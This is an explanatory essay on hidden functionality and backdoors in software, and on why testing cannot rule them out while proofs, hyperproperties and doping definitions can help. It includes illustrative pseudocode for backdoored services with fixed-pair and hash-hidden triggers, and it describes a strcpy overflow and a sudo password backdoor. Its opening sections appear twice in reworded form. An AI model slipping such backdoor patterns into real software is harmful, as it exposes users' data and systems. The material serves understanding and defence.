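# Can software be shown to do only what its author says it does?

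## What it means for a program to do only what its author says

Hidden functionality is behaviour of a computer program that its author has not stated. The author may have added it deliberately or by mistake. MITRE, an American non-profit organisation, maintains a public catalogue of software weaknesses. Its entry on hidden functionality, *CWE-912*, defines it as a function that is undocumented, is not part of the specification, and cannot be reached through a command or menu that is obvious to users or administrators. Examples include a game hidden in a product and an account with a fixed password, left in to make maintenance cheaper. In another example, a wireless access point's manual gives a web page as the only way to configure it, but the device also runs a remote-login service by default. The entry also includes Java code for a payment function that authorises a credit card and then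 emails the card number to the developer.

A shop that tested that payment function with good and bad cards would get the right answer every time. But the claim that the program does nothing except authorise cards is false, and the shop could go on collecting correct authorisations for years without learning anything about that claim.

### A service that adds two numbers

A smaller program makes the difference easier to see. A customer sends a service two positive whole numbers, each below 2^63 (the limit of an ordinary signed 64-bit variable), and the service replies with a number. Its author might publish any of these statements about it:

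1. It outputs positive numbers.
2. It outputs the sum.
3. It outputs the sum, in constant time, and touches no file or network (other than the connection on which the customer asks).

A specification is a statement of this kind made exact enough to decide whether any given behaviour is allowed. Being exact takes some work even here, because the sum of two numbers close to 2^63 is too large for the variable, and on most machines an unchecked addition then wraps round to a negative number. If the author never thought of that case, the program has accidental hidden functionality under all three statements.

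Now suppose the author is dishonest, publishes only the first statement, and writes this:

    saved := 1
    for each request (a, b):
        if a = 60317 and b = 8824651 then
            reply with saved
        else
            saved := a
            reply with a + b

Apart from the oversized sums, every reply is a positive number, so the program satisfies its author's statement. But it also gives one customer's data to anyone who knows which two numbers to send. The pair 60317 and 8824651 is a trigger, meaning an input, date or other condition that activates a hidden function. The trigger and the hidden function form a backdoor, which is hidden functionality that somebody added on purpose for use by anyone who knows about it. Computer scientists have known about this kind of leak for half a century. *Confinement* (Hook, 2007), a set of lecture slides on a classic problem in computer security,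 lists it first among possible leaks. A service with memory can collect data, wait for its owner to call, and then return the data.

*Backdoors* (Thomas and Francillon, 2018) divides a backdoor into four components, and the adding service has all four. The input source is the customer's connection, the trigger is the pair, the payload is the instruction that fetches the saved number, and the privileged state is the one in which the caller holds something he had no right to. Removing any one of them stops the backdoor from working. The paper also distinguishes the developer's view of a system, the actual system and the user's expectation of it. A backdoor is in the developer's view and the actual system but not in the user's expectation.

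### Why trying the program out does not settle it

A customer could send about 2^126 different pairs of numbers, or 8.5 × 10^37. At a billion pairs a second, a tester would need more than 10^21 years to try them all, and a billion pairs chosen at random have roughly one chance in 10^29 of including the one that matters.

A good fuzzer, a program that generates test inputs automatically, tracks which parts of the code each input reaches and builds further inputs from those that reached something new, rather than choosing at random. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) explains that modern fuzzers can also split a comparison with a long fixed value into comparisons of single bytes, which they can guess one at a time. Such a fuzzer might well send 60317 and 8824651 before long. It would still need a way to notice that anything was wrong, because the service does not crash and its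 reply is a positive number, which is all that the author promised.

A trigger can be something other than an input, such as the date. The Underhanded C Contest's *FAQ* traces that competition back to an earlier one that asked for a short program that counts votes but miscounts them on election day. A tester on any other day sees correct totals. *Facets of Software Doping* (Barthe, D'Argenio and colleagues, 2018) gives a toy version of the software in the Volkswagen emissions scandal: the engine controller doses the exhaust properly when the throttle is at one of the positions used in the official test, and follows a different rule otherwise. More testing of the official kind would not have revealed the second rule, because the test conditions switch it off.

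In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) restate a point programmers often make, that looking for problems can prove their presence but not their absence. A handful of runs can support the claim that a program does X, but the claim that it does only X covers every input, every date and every earlier history of the machine, and a single counterexample refutes it. Where such a claim can be established at all, the way to do so is formal verification, which means proving mathematically, with a machine checking the proof, that the program meets its specification on every input.

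### What an outsider can measure

Suppose the author instead publishes the second statement, that the service outputs the sum. The program above then violates the statement, because it outputs something else when it receives the trigger. A program has functional correctness if its output meets its specification, here the author's statement, for every input.

A program that always returns the correct sum can still leak its customers' data. It could write both numbers to a file, or open a connection and send them to the author, as the payment function did with the card numbers. A less noticeable way would be to wait three milliseconds longer before replying whenever the previous customer's first number was odd. Anyone who calls the program right after a customer and times the reply would then learn one bit of that customer's data.

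An observable is anything about a running program that an outsider can measure, such as its output, timing, memory use or network traffic. A side channel is an observable that reveals information but isn't part of the program's intended output. Shmatikov's *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security* lists three ways information can leave a program: outputs the author declares, explicit storage such as files and network connections, and covert channels. Covert channels are mechanisms not meant to carry information, such as system load, locks, power consumption and the timing of events. The statement "it outputs the sum" covers only the declared outputs.

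A victim is also least likely to notice hidden functions in the other observables. Lampson pointed out in *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), the paper that began the study of such leaks, that a customer who gets wrong answers can at least use them as evidence to claim restitution. When data leaks, the customer generally has no sign that anything happened.

The third statement closes the leaks described so far, and it introduces a new kind of requirement. "Constant time" means that the service takes equally long over every request. If T(a, b) is the time it takes to process the pair a and b, then T(a, b) = T(c, d) for all a, b, c and d. No single run can violate this requirement, because a reply after five milliseconds is wrong only if another reply takes a different time. Finkbeiner (2025) writes in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* that one must judge all requirements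 about the flow of information on several executions together. The standard example is noninterference. Nothing leaks from customer A to customer B if, whatever A does, B observes the same things as when the service is run again without A's actions.

Replacing a component with another that gives only permitted answers can still open a leak. *Putting Strong Linearizability in Context* (2019) gives an example with a stack, a store that returns the last item put into it. A small program keeps a secret as long as it uses an idealised stack in which each operation happens in one indivisible step. If that stack is replaced with a published one built for several processes at once, whoever controls the order in which the processes run can extract the secret, even though the published stack correctly implements the ideal one by the usual standard.

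Even the third statement leaves out memory use and power consumption. A service could set aside a large block of memory after an odd number and a small one after an even number, and another program on the same machine could detect the difference. If the author adds memory to the list, a challenger can think of something else that is missing. "Nothing but the sum" therefore has a definite meaning only once someone has specified which observables count.

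The choice of what to observe also matters when searching for backdoors. ROSA, the tool that Kokkonis and Marcozzi's group built, looks at system calls, the requests by which a program asks the operating system to open a file, start another program or send data. Their example is a backdoor in sudo, a Unix command that runs other commands with someone else's privileges. The altered version accepts the password "let_me_in" from anybody. An ordinary wrong password leads to an error message, while this one starts a program, so the system calls differ. System calls are a sensible observable for backdoors that give access to the machine. ROSA would probably miss the adding service that replies with a saved number, because that service reads a request and sends a reply just as it does when it returns the correct sum.

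### The same line as bug and as backdoor

Some hidden functions, unlike the `if` in the dishonest service, look like ordinary mistakes. Suppose the service, written in C, sets aside room for 80 characters and copies the customer's request into it with the line `strcpy(buffer, request)`. `strcpy` copies until it reaches an end marker, without checking how much room there is. A longer request overwrites neighbouring memory, and a carefully composed one can make the machine execute instructions that the sender chose. (A proof of even the weak first statement would exclude this line if it covered every possible request, since the sender could make the service reply with zero.) Programmers have written such lines by accident many times, and a programmer who planned to send the long request himself would write the same line.

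Security researchers use the term "bugdoor", which *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024) defines as a backdoor that one can plausibly argue was a genuine bug. GitHub's security report *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021) says that a good backdoor can be indistinguishable from a normal programming mistake. In their framework, Thomas and Francillon class a backdoor as intentional when the code leads openly from trigger to payload. If the way in looks like a bug, they find no technical difference between a deniable backdoor and an accidental vulnerability, and the only evidence left is circumstantial: who made the change, in which version, and whether there was a legitimate reason for it.

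I would not rely too heavily even on the open cases. Somebody certainly meant to write a fixed password into a router, but manufacturers often say such passwords were debugging aids they forgot to remove, and sometimes that must be true.

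## What it means for a program to do only what its author says

Hidden functionality is behaviour of a computer program that lies outside what its author has stated, whether it was added on purpose or by mistake. *CWE-912*, an entry in the public catalogue of software weaknesses maintained by the American non-profit MITRE, defines it as a function that is undocumented, is not part of the specification, and cannot be reached through a command or menu that is obvious to users or administrators. Its examples include a game hidden in a product, an account with a fixed password left in to make maintenance cheaper, and a wireless access point that runs a remote-login service by default, although its manual gives a web page as the only way to configure it. Another example is a few lines of Java in which a payment function authorises a credit card and then emails the card number to the developer.

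A shop that tested that payment function with good and bad cards would get the right answer every time. The program does authorise cards, but the claim that it does nothing else is false, and the shop could collect correct authorisations for years without learning anything about that claim.

### A service that adds two numbers

A smaller program makes the difference easier to see. A customer sends a service two positive whole numbers, each below 2^63 (the limit of an ordinary signed 64-bit variable), and the service replies with a number. Its author might publish any of these statements about it:

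1. It outputs positive numbers.
2. It outputs the sum.
3. It outputs the sum, in constant time, and touches no file or network (other than the connection on which the customer asks).

A specification is a statement of this kind made exact enough to settle whether it allows any given behaviour. Even for addition, being exact takes some work, because the sum of two numbers close to 2^63 is too large for the variable, and on most machines an unchecked addition then wraps round to a negative number. If the author never thought of that case, the program has accidental hidden functionality under all three statements.

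Now suppose the author is dishonest, publishes only the first statement, and writes this:

    saved := 1
    for each request (a, b):
        if a = 60317 and b = 8824651 then
            reply with saved
        else
            saved := a
            reply with a + b

Every reply is a positive number (leaving the oversized sums aside), so the program fits the statement. It also gives one customer's data to anyone who knows which two numbers to send. The pair 60317 and 8824651 is a trigger, meaning the input, date or other condition that sets off a hidden function. The arrangement is a backdoor, meaning hidden functionality that somebody put in on purpose so that a person who knows of it can use it. *Confinement* (Hook, 2007), a set of lecture slides on a 1973 paper, puts this old trick first in the list of possible leaks. A service with memory can collect data, wait for its owner to call,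 and then return the data.

Thomas and Francillon (2018), in *Backdoors*, divide such backdoors into four components, and the adding service has all four. They are an input source (the customer's connection), a trigger (the pair), a payload (the instruction that fetches the saved number) and a privileged state, in which the caller holds something he had no right to. If any one is removed, the backdoor stops working. They also distinguish the developer's view of a system, the actual system and the user's expectation of it. A backdoor exists in the developer's view and the actual system but not in the user's expectation.

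### Why trying the program out does not settle it

A customer could send about 2^126 pairs of numbers, or 8.5 × 10^37. Testing them all at a billion pairs a second would take more than 10^21 years, and a billion pairs chosen at random have roughly one chance in 10^29 of including the one that matters.

Instead of choosing inputs at random, good testers can use a fuzzer, a program that generates test inputs automatically. It tracks which parts of the code each input reaches and builds further inputs from those that reached something new. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) explains that modern fuzzers can also split a comparison with a long fixed value into single-byte comparisons and guess the bytes one at a time. Such a tool might well send 60317 and 8824651 before long. But it would still need a way to recognise that the reply is wrong, because the service does not crash and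 the reply is a positive number, which is all the author promised.

A trigger need not be an input. The Underhanded C Contest's *FAQ* traces the contest to an earlier one, in which entrants had to write a simple vote-counting program that miscounts on election day. A tester sees correct totals on any other day. *Facets of Software Doping* (Barthe, D'Argenio and colleagues, 2018) gives a toy version of the software in the Volkswagen emissions scandal. The engine controller doses the exhaust properly whenever the throttle is at one of the positions used in the official test, and follows a different rule otherwise. More tests of the official kind would not reveal the hidden function, because the test conditions switch it off.

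Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) point out in *Provably safe systems* that looking for problems can prove their presence but not their absence. A handful of runs can support the claim that a program does X, but the claim that it does nothing but X covers every input, every date and every earlier history of the machine, so a single counterexample refutes it. Formal verification aims to establish claims of this form with a machine-checked mathematical proof that the program meets its specification on every input.

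### What an outsider can measure

Suppose the author instead publishes the second statement, that the service outputs the sum. The program above no longer satisfies the author's statement, because it outputs something else when it receives the trigger. A program has functional correctness if its output matches the specification for every input.

The program can still leak its customers' data even if every reply is correct. It could return the correct sum and also write both numbers to a file, or open a connection and send them to the author, much as the payment function did with the card numbers. Or it could wait three milliseconds longer before replying whenever the previous customer's first number was odd. Anyone who called right after a customer and timed the reply precisely enough could then tell whether that customer's first number was odd.

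An observable is anything about a running program that an outsider can measure, including its output, timing, memory use and network traffic. A side channel is an observable that reveals information but is not part of the program's intended output. Shmatikov, in *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security*, divides the ways information can leave a program into outputs the author declares, explicit storage such as files and network connections, and covert channels. Covert channels are mechanisms not intended for carrying information, such as system load, locks, power consumption and the timing of events. The statement "it outputs the sum" covers only the declared outputs.

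Leaks are also harder for a victim to notice than wrong answers. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), the paper behind Hook's slides, Lampson pointed out that a customer who gets wrong answers can use them as evidence to claim restitution, while a customer whose data has leaked generally has no sign that anything happened.

The third statement closes the leaks described so far and introduces a new kind of requirement. "Constant time" means that the service takes as long over one request as over any other. If T(a, b) is the time it takes over the pair a and b, then T(a, b) = T(c, d) for all a, b, c and d. No single run can violate this, because a reply after five milliseconds is neither right nor wrong until it is compared with another reply. Finkbeiner (2025), in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties*, makes the same point about information-flow requirements in general, which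 have to be judged on several executions together. The standard example is noninterference, which compares a run of the service with a second run that leaves out everything customer A did. If customer B observes the same things in both, whatever A did, nothing has leaked from A to B.

A program can leak a secret even when each of its components gives only permitted answers. *Putting Strong Linearizability in Context* (2019) gives an example with a stack, which returns the most recently added item first. A small program does not reveal its secret when it uses an ideal stack, where each operation happens in one indivisible step. If it instead uses a published stack built for several processes at once, whoever controls the order in which the processes run can extract the secret, even though the published stack correctly implements the ideal one by the usual standard.

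Even the third statement leaves out memory use and power consumption. A service could allocate a large block of memory after an odd number and a small one after an even number, and another program on the same machine might be able to measure the difference. The author can add memory use to the list, but a challenger can then think of something else. "Nothing but the sum" has a definite meaning only after someone specifies which observables count.

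The choice of what to observe also matters when searching for backdoors. The tool that Kokkonis and colleagues built looks at system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, start another program or send data. Their example is a backdoor in sudo, a Unix command that runs other commands with someone else's privileges. The altered version accepts the password "let_me_in" from anybody. An ordinary wrong password leads to an error message, while this one starts a program, so the system calls differ. Observing system calls is sensible for backdoors that give access to the machine. The tool would probably miss the adding service that replies with a saved number, because the service reads a request and sends a reply exactly as it does for any other pair of numbers.

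### The same line as bug and as backdoor

The `if` in the dishonest service is hard to explain as a mistake, but other hidden functions look like ordinary carelessness. A service written in C might set aside room for 80 characters and copy the customer's request into it with the line `strcpy(buffer, request)`. That instruction copies until it reaches an end marker, without checking whether the request fits. A longer request overwrites neighbouring memory, and a carefully composed one can make the machine execute instructions that the sender chose. Programmers have written such lines by accident many times, and a programmer who planned to send the long request himself later would write the same line. Even a proof of the weak first statement would rule out this flaw if it covered every possible request, since the sender could use the flaw to make the service reply with zero.

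Security researchers call this a bugdoor. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (2024) defines it as a backdoor that one can plausibly argue was a genuine bug. GitHub acknowledges in its security report, *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), that a good backdoor can be indistinguishable from a normal programming mistake. Thomas and Francillon class a backdoor as intentional if the code leads openly from trigger to payload. But if the way in looks like a bug, they too find no technical difference between a deniable backdoor and an accidental vulnerability, leaving only circumstantial evidence: who made the change, in which version, and whether there was a legitimate reason for it.

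Whoever writes a fixed password into a router certainly means to, but may not intend it as a backdoor. Manufacturers often explain such passwords as debugging aids that they forgot to remove, and presumably some of them are telling the truth. Zdziarski (2016), in *Backdoor*, requires that intent, consent and access all be considered before a mechanism is called a backdoor, so two identical programs could differ in whether they contain one.

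Barthe and colleagues ran into this difficulty with the iPhone. After a software update, iPhones that an unauthorised shop had repaired stopped working. This looked like deliberate punishment but was a fault, which Apple fixed. The phones would have behaved the same way if the designers had wanted to punish those customers. So the group included intent in its informal description of the problem but left it out of its definitions, which compare behaviour with a contract.

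Anyone who wants to test a program, rather than judge its author's guilt, has to compare what it does with what the author said it does. Harmless extras therefore count as hidden functionality until the author writes them down. The result also depends heavily on how much the statement specifies. If an author promises only that the program will output positive numbers, a challenger can object to almost nothing it does.

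### Source code, compiled program, machine

*A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994) documents 50 actual flaws. Its scheme, as *Seven Pernicious Kingdoms* summarises it, records how and when each flaw got in and where in the system it sits. In the adding service, a flaw could sit in at least three places.

Programmers write source code, which people can read, so a reader would see the `if` with the two odd numbers. But customers run a file of processor instructions, which a program called a compiler produces from the source. That file can contain a branch that the source lacks, because someone replaced the file before customers downloaded it or because the compiler itself added the branch. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026), in *Not In My Git Yard*, distinguish three routes that attackers have used to put backdoors into open-source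 software: a malicious change to the public source, tampering with the release package outside the public source, and a compromised dependency, which is somebody else's code that the program uses. If an honest author of the adding service uses a library to read numbers, his statement about what the service does also covers the library's code, which he may never have read.

A program's behavior also depends on the machine that runs it. If a processor added just one pair of numbers incorrectly, the claim "it outputs the sum" would be false even if the source code and its translation were both correct. Tegmark and Omohundro mention an attack that adds a hidden capacitor to a chip; a rare instruction charges the capacitor, which eventually opens a backdoor. The trusted base of a proof about a program is everything that must work as assumed for the proof to hold for the running system. For a proof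 about source code, it normally includes the compiler and the chip.

### Three kinds of contest

People have turned these questions into competitions, which differ in what the participants know. In some, entrants write underhanded code, which is source code that looks correct to a reviewer but does something malicious. The best-known example is the Underhanded C Contest, which a professor at Binghamton University has run since 2005. The entrants know exactly what their programs do, and the judges look for the most convincing disguise.

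In a contest to find planted malice, the organisers hide malicious behaviour in software and entrants search for it. *The Next Challenge for Agentic Cybersecurity* (2026) describes a game with six hidden behaviours that the manual does not mention and that never occur in ordinary play. They produce no message or sound. Entrants have to reconstruct the logic from the compiled program and submit a sequence of moves, which a checking program replays to see which behaviours it triggers. The game also contains decoys, which are ordinary parts built from similar strange-looking code, a few with the same constants. The AI Cyber Challenge, which *ATLANTIS* (2025) describes from the side of a competing system, similarly hid vulnerabilities in real open-source projects and required teams to supply an input that triggered the fault. Because the organisers know what they planted, they can count misses,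 and if they include clean programs or decoys, they can also count false alarms. A planted control is a program of known status used to count these errors.

The remaining kind of contest tests an author's claim. An author publishes a program with a statement of what it does, and challengers earn money for finding any behaviour outside the statement. *Build It, Break It, Fix It* (2019) describes a similar contest, in which teams implement a specification and other teams attack the results using the source code, but the organisers write the specification. Teams can also earn points by showing that the organisers' own reference program contradicts the specification, which is a small version of testing an author's claim. Nobody in this kind of contest knows beforehand whether there is anything to find, so if the challengers find nothing, the organisers cannot tell from that alone whether the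 program is clean or the challengers missed something.

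## What theory rules out and what it leaves possible

A customer who cannot test every pair of numbers might hope for a checker, a program that reads other programs and reports whether they contain hidden functions. No checker can be right about every program. This follows from a theorem that Rice (1953), in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, stated for sets of numbers. In terms of programs, it concerns properties of what a program does, as opposed to how its text looks. Such a property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others lack it. Rice's theorem is that no algorithm can decide a non-trivial property of this kind correctly for all programs. (Whether the source contains an `if` is a question about the text, and any editor can answer it.)

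### Rice's theorem, with hidden functions as the property

The proof starts from the halting problem. Turing showed in the 1930s that no program can tell, for every program P and input x, whether P eventually stops when it runs on x. If such a program, `halts(P, x)`, existed, a programmer could write a program D that takes the text of a program P, calls `halts(P, P)`, and then loops forever if the answer is yes and stops if it is no. If D runs on its own text, it stops exactly when `halts` has answered that it won't, so `halts` is wrong about D.

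Now suppose somebody sells a checker that reports correctly, for every adding service, whether the service always replies with the sum. Take any program P and input x, and write this service:

    n := 0
    saved := 1
    for each request (a, b):
        n := n + 1
        simulate the first n steps of P on x
        if P has stopped then
            reply with saved
        else
            saved := a
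            reply with a + b

The service answers every request, because each simulation has a limited number of steps. If P never stops on x, every reply is the sum and there is no hidden function. If P stops after a million steps, the service starts revealing a customer's number at the millionth request. The checker's result would therefore show whether P stops on x. Since P and x were arbitrary, the checker would solve the halting problem, so it cannot exist.

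Rice's general result needs only a small change to the argument. For any non-trivial property, we can assume that a program that never answers lacks it, because otherwise we can argue about the opposite property instead. Some program A has the property. We write a new program that first simulates P on x to the end and then behaves like A. This new program has the property exactly when P stops on x.

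The theorem assumes unlimited memory. A real machine has a finite number of states, so a checker could in principle follow a program until a state repeats. But one kilobyte of memory has about 10^2466 possible states, which is too many for this method to help a reviewer.

### What the theorem does not forbid

The theorem rules out a checker that gives a correct yes or no for every program. A customer usually wants to know about one program, and its author can write it so that the answer is easy to prove. If the body of the loop is just `reply with a + b`, the proof takes one line.

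A recipient can also reject every program that arrives without a proof. If the proofs are sound, this rule never accepts a bad program, but it rejects some clean ones. Whatever proof system the recipient uses, some clean programs have no proof in it. If every clean service of the kind above had one, a checker could search through all possible proofs and, in parallel, through all possible sequences of requests for a wrong reply. One of the two searches would always succeed, so the checker could always tell whether such a service was clean, which Rice's theorem shows is impossible. Honest authors have little reason to write clean programs that have no proof, so for them the rule mainly adds the work of finding proofs.

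Another way to avoid this limit is to restrict the language. The argument above applies only if a service can simulate an arbitrary program for as long as it takes. If jumps may only go forward, each instruction runs at most once per request, so the program always finishes. If inputs also have a fixed size, there are finitely many cases to check to determine whether the program always replies with the sum. The check may still be infeasible, because a program without loops can contain a great deal of arithmetic.

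### Proof-carrying code

In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) describe a working system they built to let users install their own programs in the kernel, the part of an operating system that has full control of the machine. The recipient publishes a safety policy. The program's author sends the compiled program with a proof that it obeys the policy, and the recipient checks the proof and runs the program only if the proof is valid. Necula and Lee call this proof-carrying code.

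One of their examples is a table inside the kernel that holds two words for each user, a tag and a data word. A user's program may read both words in its own entry, but may write to the data word only if the tag is not zero. Suppose a user submits this:

    load the tag
    if the tag is zero, skip the next instruction
    store a new value in the data word

The recipient's software goes through the program from the last instruction to the first, collecting what has to be true for each step to be safe. The store requires permission to write to the data word. The skip weakens this to a requirement that applies only when the tag is not zero, and the load adds permission to read the tag. The result is a formula:

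    may_read(tag) and (tag ≠ 0 implies may_write(data))

This follows directly from the policy, so the proof is short. If an attacker deletes the second line after the author has written the proof, the recipient's software computes a different formula, `may_read(tag) and may_write(data)`. The old proof doesn't prove this formula, and no new proof can, because the policy forbids writing when the tag is zero. The recipient's software accepts an altered program only if it still obeys the policy.

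Necula and Lee tested the method on packet filters, small programs that select network traffic for an application. Each proof was checked once, which took 1 to 3 milliseconds, and the filter then ran without further checks. Necula reports in *Proof-Carrying Code* that these filters were ten times faster than equivalent ones in the usual interpreted language, which forbids loops and checks memory accesses as the filter runs. He also points out that a simple version of the proof checker takes only a couple of pages of code, which matters because the recipient has to trust both the checker and the policy.

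Finding proofs is much harder than checking them. An automatic prover found them for the packet filters, which have no loops. For a program with loops, somebody generally has to supply invariants, which are statements that remain true on every pass through the loop. Necula named this as the main difficulty. He doubted that the approach would scale to programs of realistic size, and hoped instead for compilers that produce a proof as they translate. But the program's author does all this work, and the author knows why the program is supposed to be right and can change it if the proof is too hard.

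The policy for the filters covered memory, so a proof that a filter reads only permitted addresses does not show that it selects the right packets. The dishonest adding service, which uses only its own memory, could carry a valid proof of the same kind. Proof-carrying code lets the recipient write the policy. If the software's author writes the statement to be proved instead, the recipient can check the proof just as easily, but must also judge whether the statement was worth proving.

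### A trigger behind a hash

In the first dishonest service, the pair 60317 and 8824651 was visible in the source, where a reader or a fuzzer could pick it up. A more careful author would use a cryptographic hash function. This turns any input into a number of fixed length, say 256 bits, and nobody knows a way to find an input with a given hash that is much faster than guessing. The author chooses a secret pair, computes its hash K at home, and puts only K in the program:

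    if hash(a, b) = K then
        reply with saved
    else
        saved := a
        reply with a + b

Guessing one byte at a time no longer works, because a pair whose hash matches K in the first byte is no closer to the secret pair than any other.

Suppose the service accepts any two positive 64-bit numbers and has room for their sum. There are about 2^128 pairs, or 3.4 × 10^38. A billion tests a second for a year would cover 3.2 × 10^16 pairs, or about one in 10^22. A million machines testing at that rate for a million years would have roughly one chance in ten billion of hitting the secret pair.

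The tests would still give excellent protection against accidental errors spread over the inputs. If a year of randomly chosen pairs produces no wrong reply, a statistician can conclude with 95% confidence that fewer than about one pair in 10^16 goes wrong, so an ordinary customer would almost never encounter an error. But as many as roughly 3 × 10^22 pairs could still trigger a wrong reply, and a backdoor can be used with only one trigger.

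Somebody who tries to prove that the service outputs the sum doesn't have to find the pair. Working backwards through the `if`, as in the kernel example, gives two things to prove:

    hash(a, b) = K  implies  saved = a + b
    hash(a, b) ≠ K  implies  a + b = a + b

The second is trivially true. To prove the first, the author would have to show either that `saved` always equals the sum or that no pair has the hash K. Both are false, so no proof exists, and the recipient rejects the program without learning which pair triggers the hidden function.

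The recipient doesn't even learn whether such a pair exists. If an author picked K at random, almost certainly no pair would match it and the program would be clean, but the recipient would still reject the program. An honest author can avoid the rejection by deleting the line.

The rejection depends on the statement being "it outputs the sum". If the author promises only that the output is positive, the first line to prove becomes "hash(a, b) = K implies saved > 0". This is easy to prove because `saved` starts at 1 and afterwards holds only positive numbers from customers. The backdoored service would then have a valid proof.

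### A reviewer who has only the code

The hash conceals the trigger, but a reader can still see a suspicious `if`. An obfuscator might hide that too. In *On the (Im)possibility of Obfuscating Programs*, Barak, Goldreich and colleagues define an obfuscator as a compiler that turns a program into another that has the same function but is in some sense unintelligible. In the strictest version, the new program is a "virtual black box", which means that anything a reader can efficiently work out from its code, he could also work out by running it on inputs of his choice. Reading the code would then be no better than testing, and the odds of finding the trigger would be those just calculated. Barak and colleagues mention that such an obfuscator would make possible, among other things, analogues of Rice's theorem for efficient algorithms.

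"On the (Im)possibility of Obfuscating Programs" proves that no obfuscator can make every program's code reveal nothing more than running the program would. It constructs programs whose code, however disguised, gives away a secret that nobody could efficiently extract by running them. This gives a reviewer limited reassurance, because a service that adds numbers is not one of those programs, and a weaker kind of obfuscation would be enough to disguise it.

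Cryptographers have defined one such kind, extractability obfuscation. It requires that anyone who can tell the obfuscated versions of two programs apart can also find an input on which the programs differ. If `saved` is fixed at some number for simplicity, the honest adding service and the one with the hash differ only on the secret pair. A reviewer who could tell which of the two he had received could therefore find that pair, which the hash makes infeasible. Researchers have proposed ways to build obfuscators of this general type, though their security rests on unproved assumptions.

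A recipient can still insist on a proof. An honest author can supply one even if the code is unreadable, but an author who has added a backdoor cannot. Obfuscation is therefore a serious problem for a reviewer who must reach a verdict by reading the code, but much less of one for a recipient who can refuse software that comes without a proof.

### Why one run cannot show a leak

A proof that every reply is the correct sum still leaves timing, and a claim about leaks through timing has a different logical form. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, describe a run of a system by its trace, the sequence of states it passes through, and describe the system as the set T of all traces it can produce. An ordinary requirement is a set P of acceptable traces, and the system meets it if

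    T ⊆ P

One of their examples is a rule that a system may not write to the network after reading from a file. An inspector can apply it to each trace separately: a trace fails if it has a file read at some moment i and a network write at a later moment j. A hyperproperty is a set H of acceptable systems, and the system meets it if

    T ∈ H

Noninterference, the requirement that what customer A does has no effect on what customer B observes, is a hyperproperty. For a deterministic system, Clarkson and Schneider's formula for it amounts to this:

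    for every t in T there is a t′ in T such that
        t′ contains no secret inputs, and
        t and t′ contain the same public events

Here A's requests are the secret inputs, and the public events are everything B sends and receives, including the time each reply takes.

No requirement on single traces can do the same job. Suppose that B always sends the same pair and gets the right sum, and consider three services that differ only in how long B waits:

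| | A sends nothing | A sends an odd number |
|---|---|---|
| First service | 2 ms | 2 ms |
| Second service | 5 ms | 5 ms |
| Third service | 2 ms | 5 ms |

The first two services have no leaks, but the third does. A rule P that checks one run at a time and accepts exactly the services without leaks would have to accept both runs of the first service and both runs of the second. The third service consists of one run from each, so P would wrongly accept it too.

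A log of correct and reasonably prompt replies is therefore no evidence that a service keeps secrets. A tester has to compare runs that differ only in the secret, and with 2^128 possible secrets there are far more pairs of runs than runs. Like secrecy, the requirement that the mean response time over all executions stay below one second is a hyperproperty, because whether one slow reply is acceptable depends on all the others.

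Proofs can still handle such requirements. Rival (2023), in *Analysis of security properties*, writes noninterference for a program as a condition on two starting memories, m0 and m1:

    if m0 and m1 agree on all public variables,
    then the results of running the program from m0 and from m1
    agree on all public variables

To prove this, one can write the program out twice, with different variable names in the second copy, and run the copies one after the other. The condition is then an ordinary statement about a single run of the doubled program. This technique, called self-composition, covers timing if one of the public variables counts the steps.

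### Leaks through the choices a specification allows

Clarkson and Schneider also show that a program can satisfy a secure specification and still leak everything. Their specification lets a system output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. The possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is, so an observer learns nothing from which outputs are possible. But a program that always outputs the secret bit, and so reveals it on every run, still satisfies the specification, because the specification allows each of its outputs.

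Programmers usually develop software by refinement, which means starting from a loose specification and narrowing it down. If every trace the specification allows meets an ordinary requirement, so does every trace of the refined program, because the program produces only some of those traces. But refinement does not always preserve hyperproperties, and according to Kestrel Institute's *Hyperproperties Project*, it can turn a secure system into an insecure one.

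Even specifications much stricter than "it outputs positive numbers" leave a program enough freedom to leak data. Suppose a search service must return the 20 matching records and may list them in any order. There are 20! possible orders, about 2.4 × 10^18, so the service can use the order to encode 61 bits of another customer's data in every reply. A functional correctness proof against that specification would still succeed.

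An author can prevent this by fixing the order, for instance alphabetically, so that the program can't vary it. The author would have to fix every other observable too, which is hard for timing. Alternatively, the author can state noninterference as a separate requirement and prove that the finished program satisfies it. Some hyperproperties survive refinement, such as observational determinism, which requires any two runs that begin alike for a public observer to keep looking alike. It survives because refinement only removes runs, and removing runs can't create two that disagree.

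### A formal definition of clean software

All these methods need a specification, and a manufacturer who wants to cheat is unlikely to publish a helpful one. *Is your software on dope?* (D'Argenio, Barthe and colleagues, 2017) therefore defines clean software by comparing a program's behaviour in different situations, so nobody has to specify the correct output in full. The paper uses "doping" to mean hidden functionality that serves the manufacturer against the interests of the user or society.

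They begin with a printer that works only with its maker's cartridges. Let S(p)(i) be the output of program S with cartridge p and document i. The program is clean if

    S(p)(i) = S(p′)(i)

for all compatible cartridges p and p′ and all standard documents i. The restriction to standard documents lets a manufacturer offer a new file format that needs a special cartridge. Somebody has to draw up a contract that fixes which cartridges are compatible and which documents are standard, and outside that contract the definition permits anything.

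Because of that gap, the first definition can miss cheating by a program like Volkswagen's engine software. D'Argenio and colleagues give numbers for the toy engine controller. The throttle position x lies between 0 and 2, and the official test covers positions up to 1. Emissions are x³ / (2 × dose), where the dose is the amount of cleaning fluid. The honest controller always injects x², so emissions are x/2. The cheating one injects x² up to position 1 and only x beyond it, which raises emissions there to x²/2. At full throttle, the honest car emits 1 and the cheating car emits 2. If the standard inputs are the test positions, both controllers satisfy the first definition.

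The group's next definition extends the comparison to inputs near the standard ones. A program is robustly clean if, for every standard input i and every input i′ (standard or not),

    distance(i, i′) ≤ κ_in  implies  distance(output for i, output for i′) ≤ κ_out

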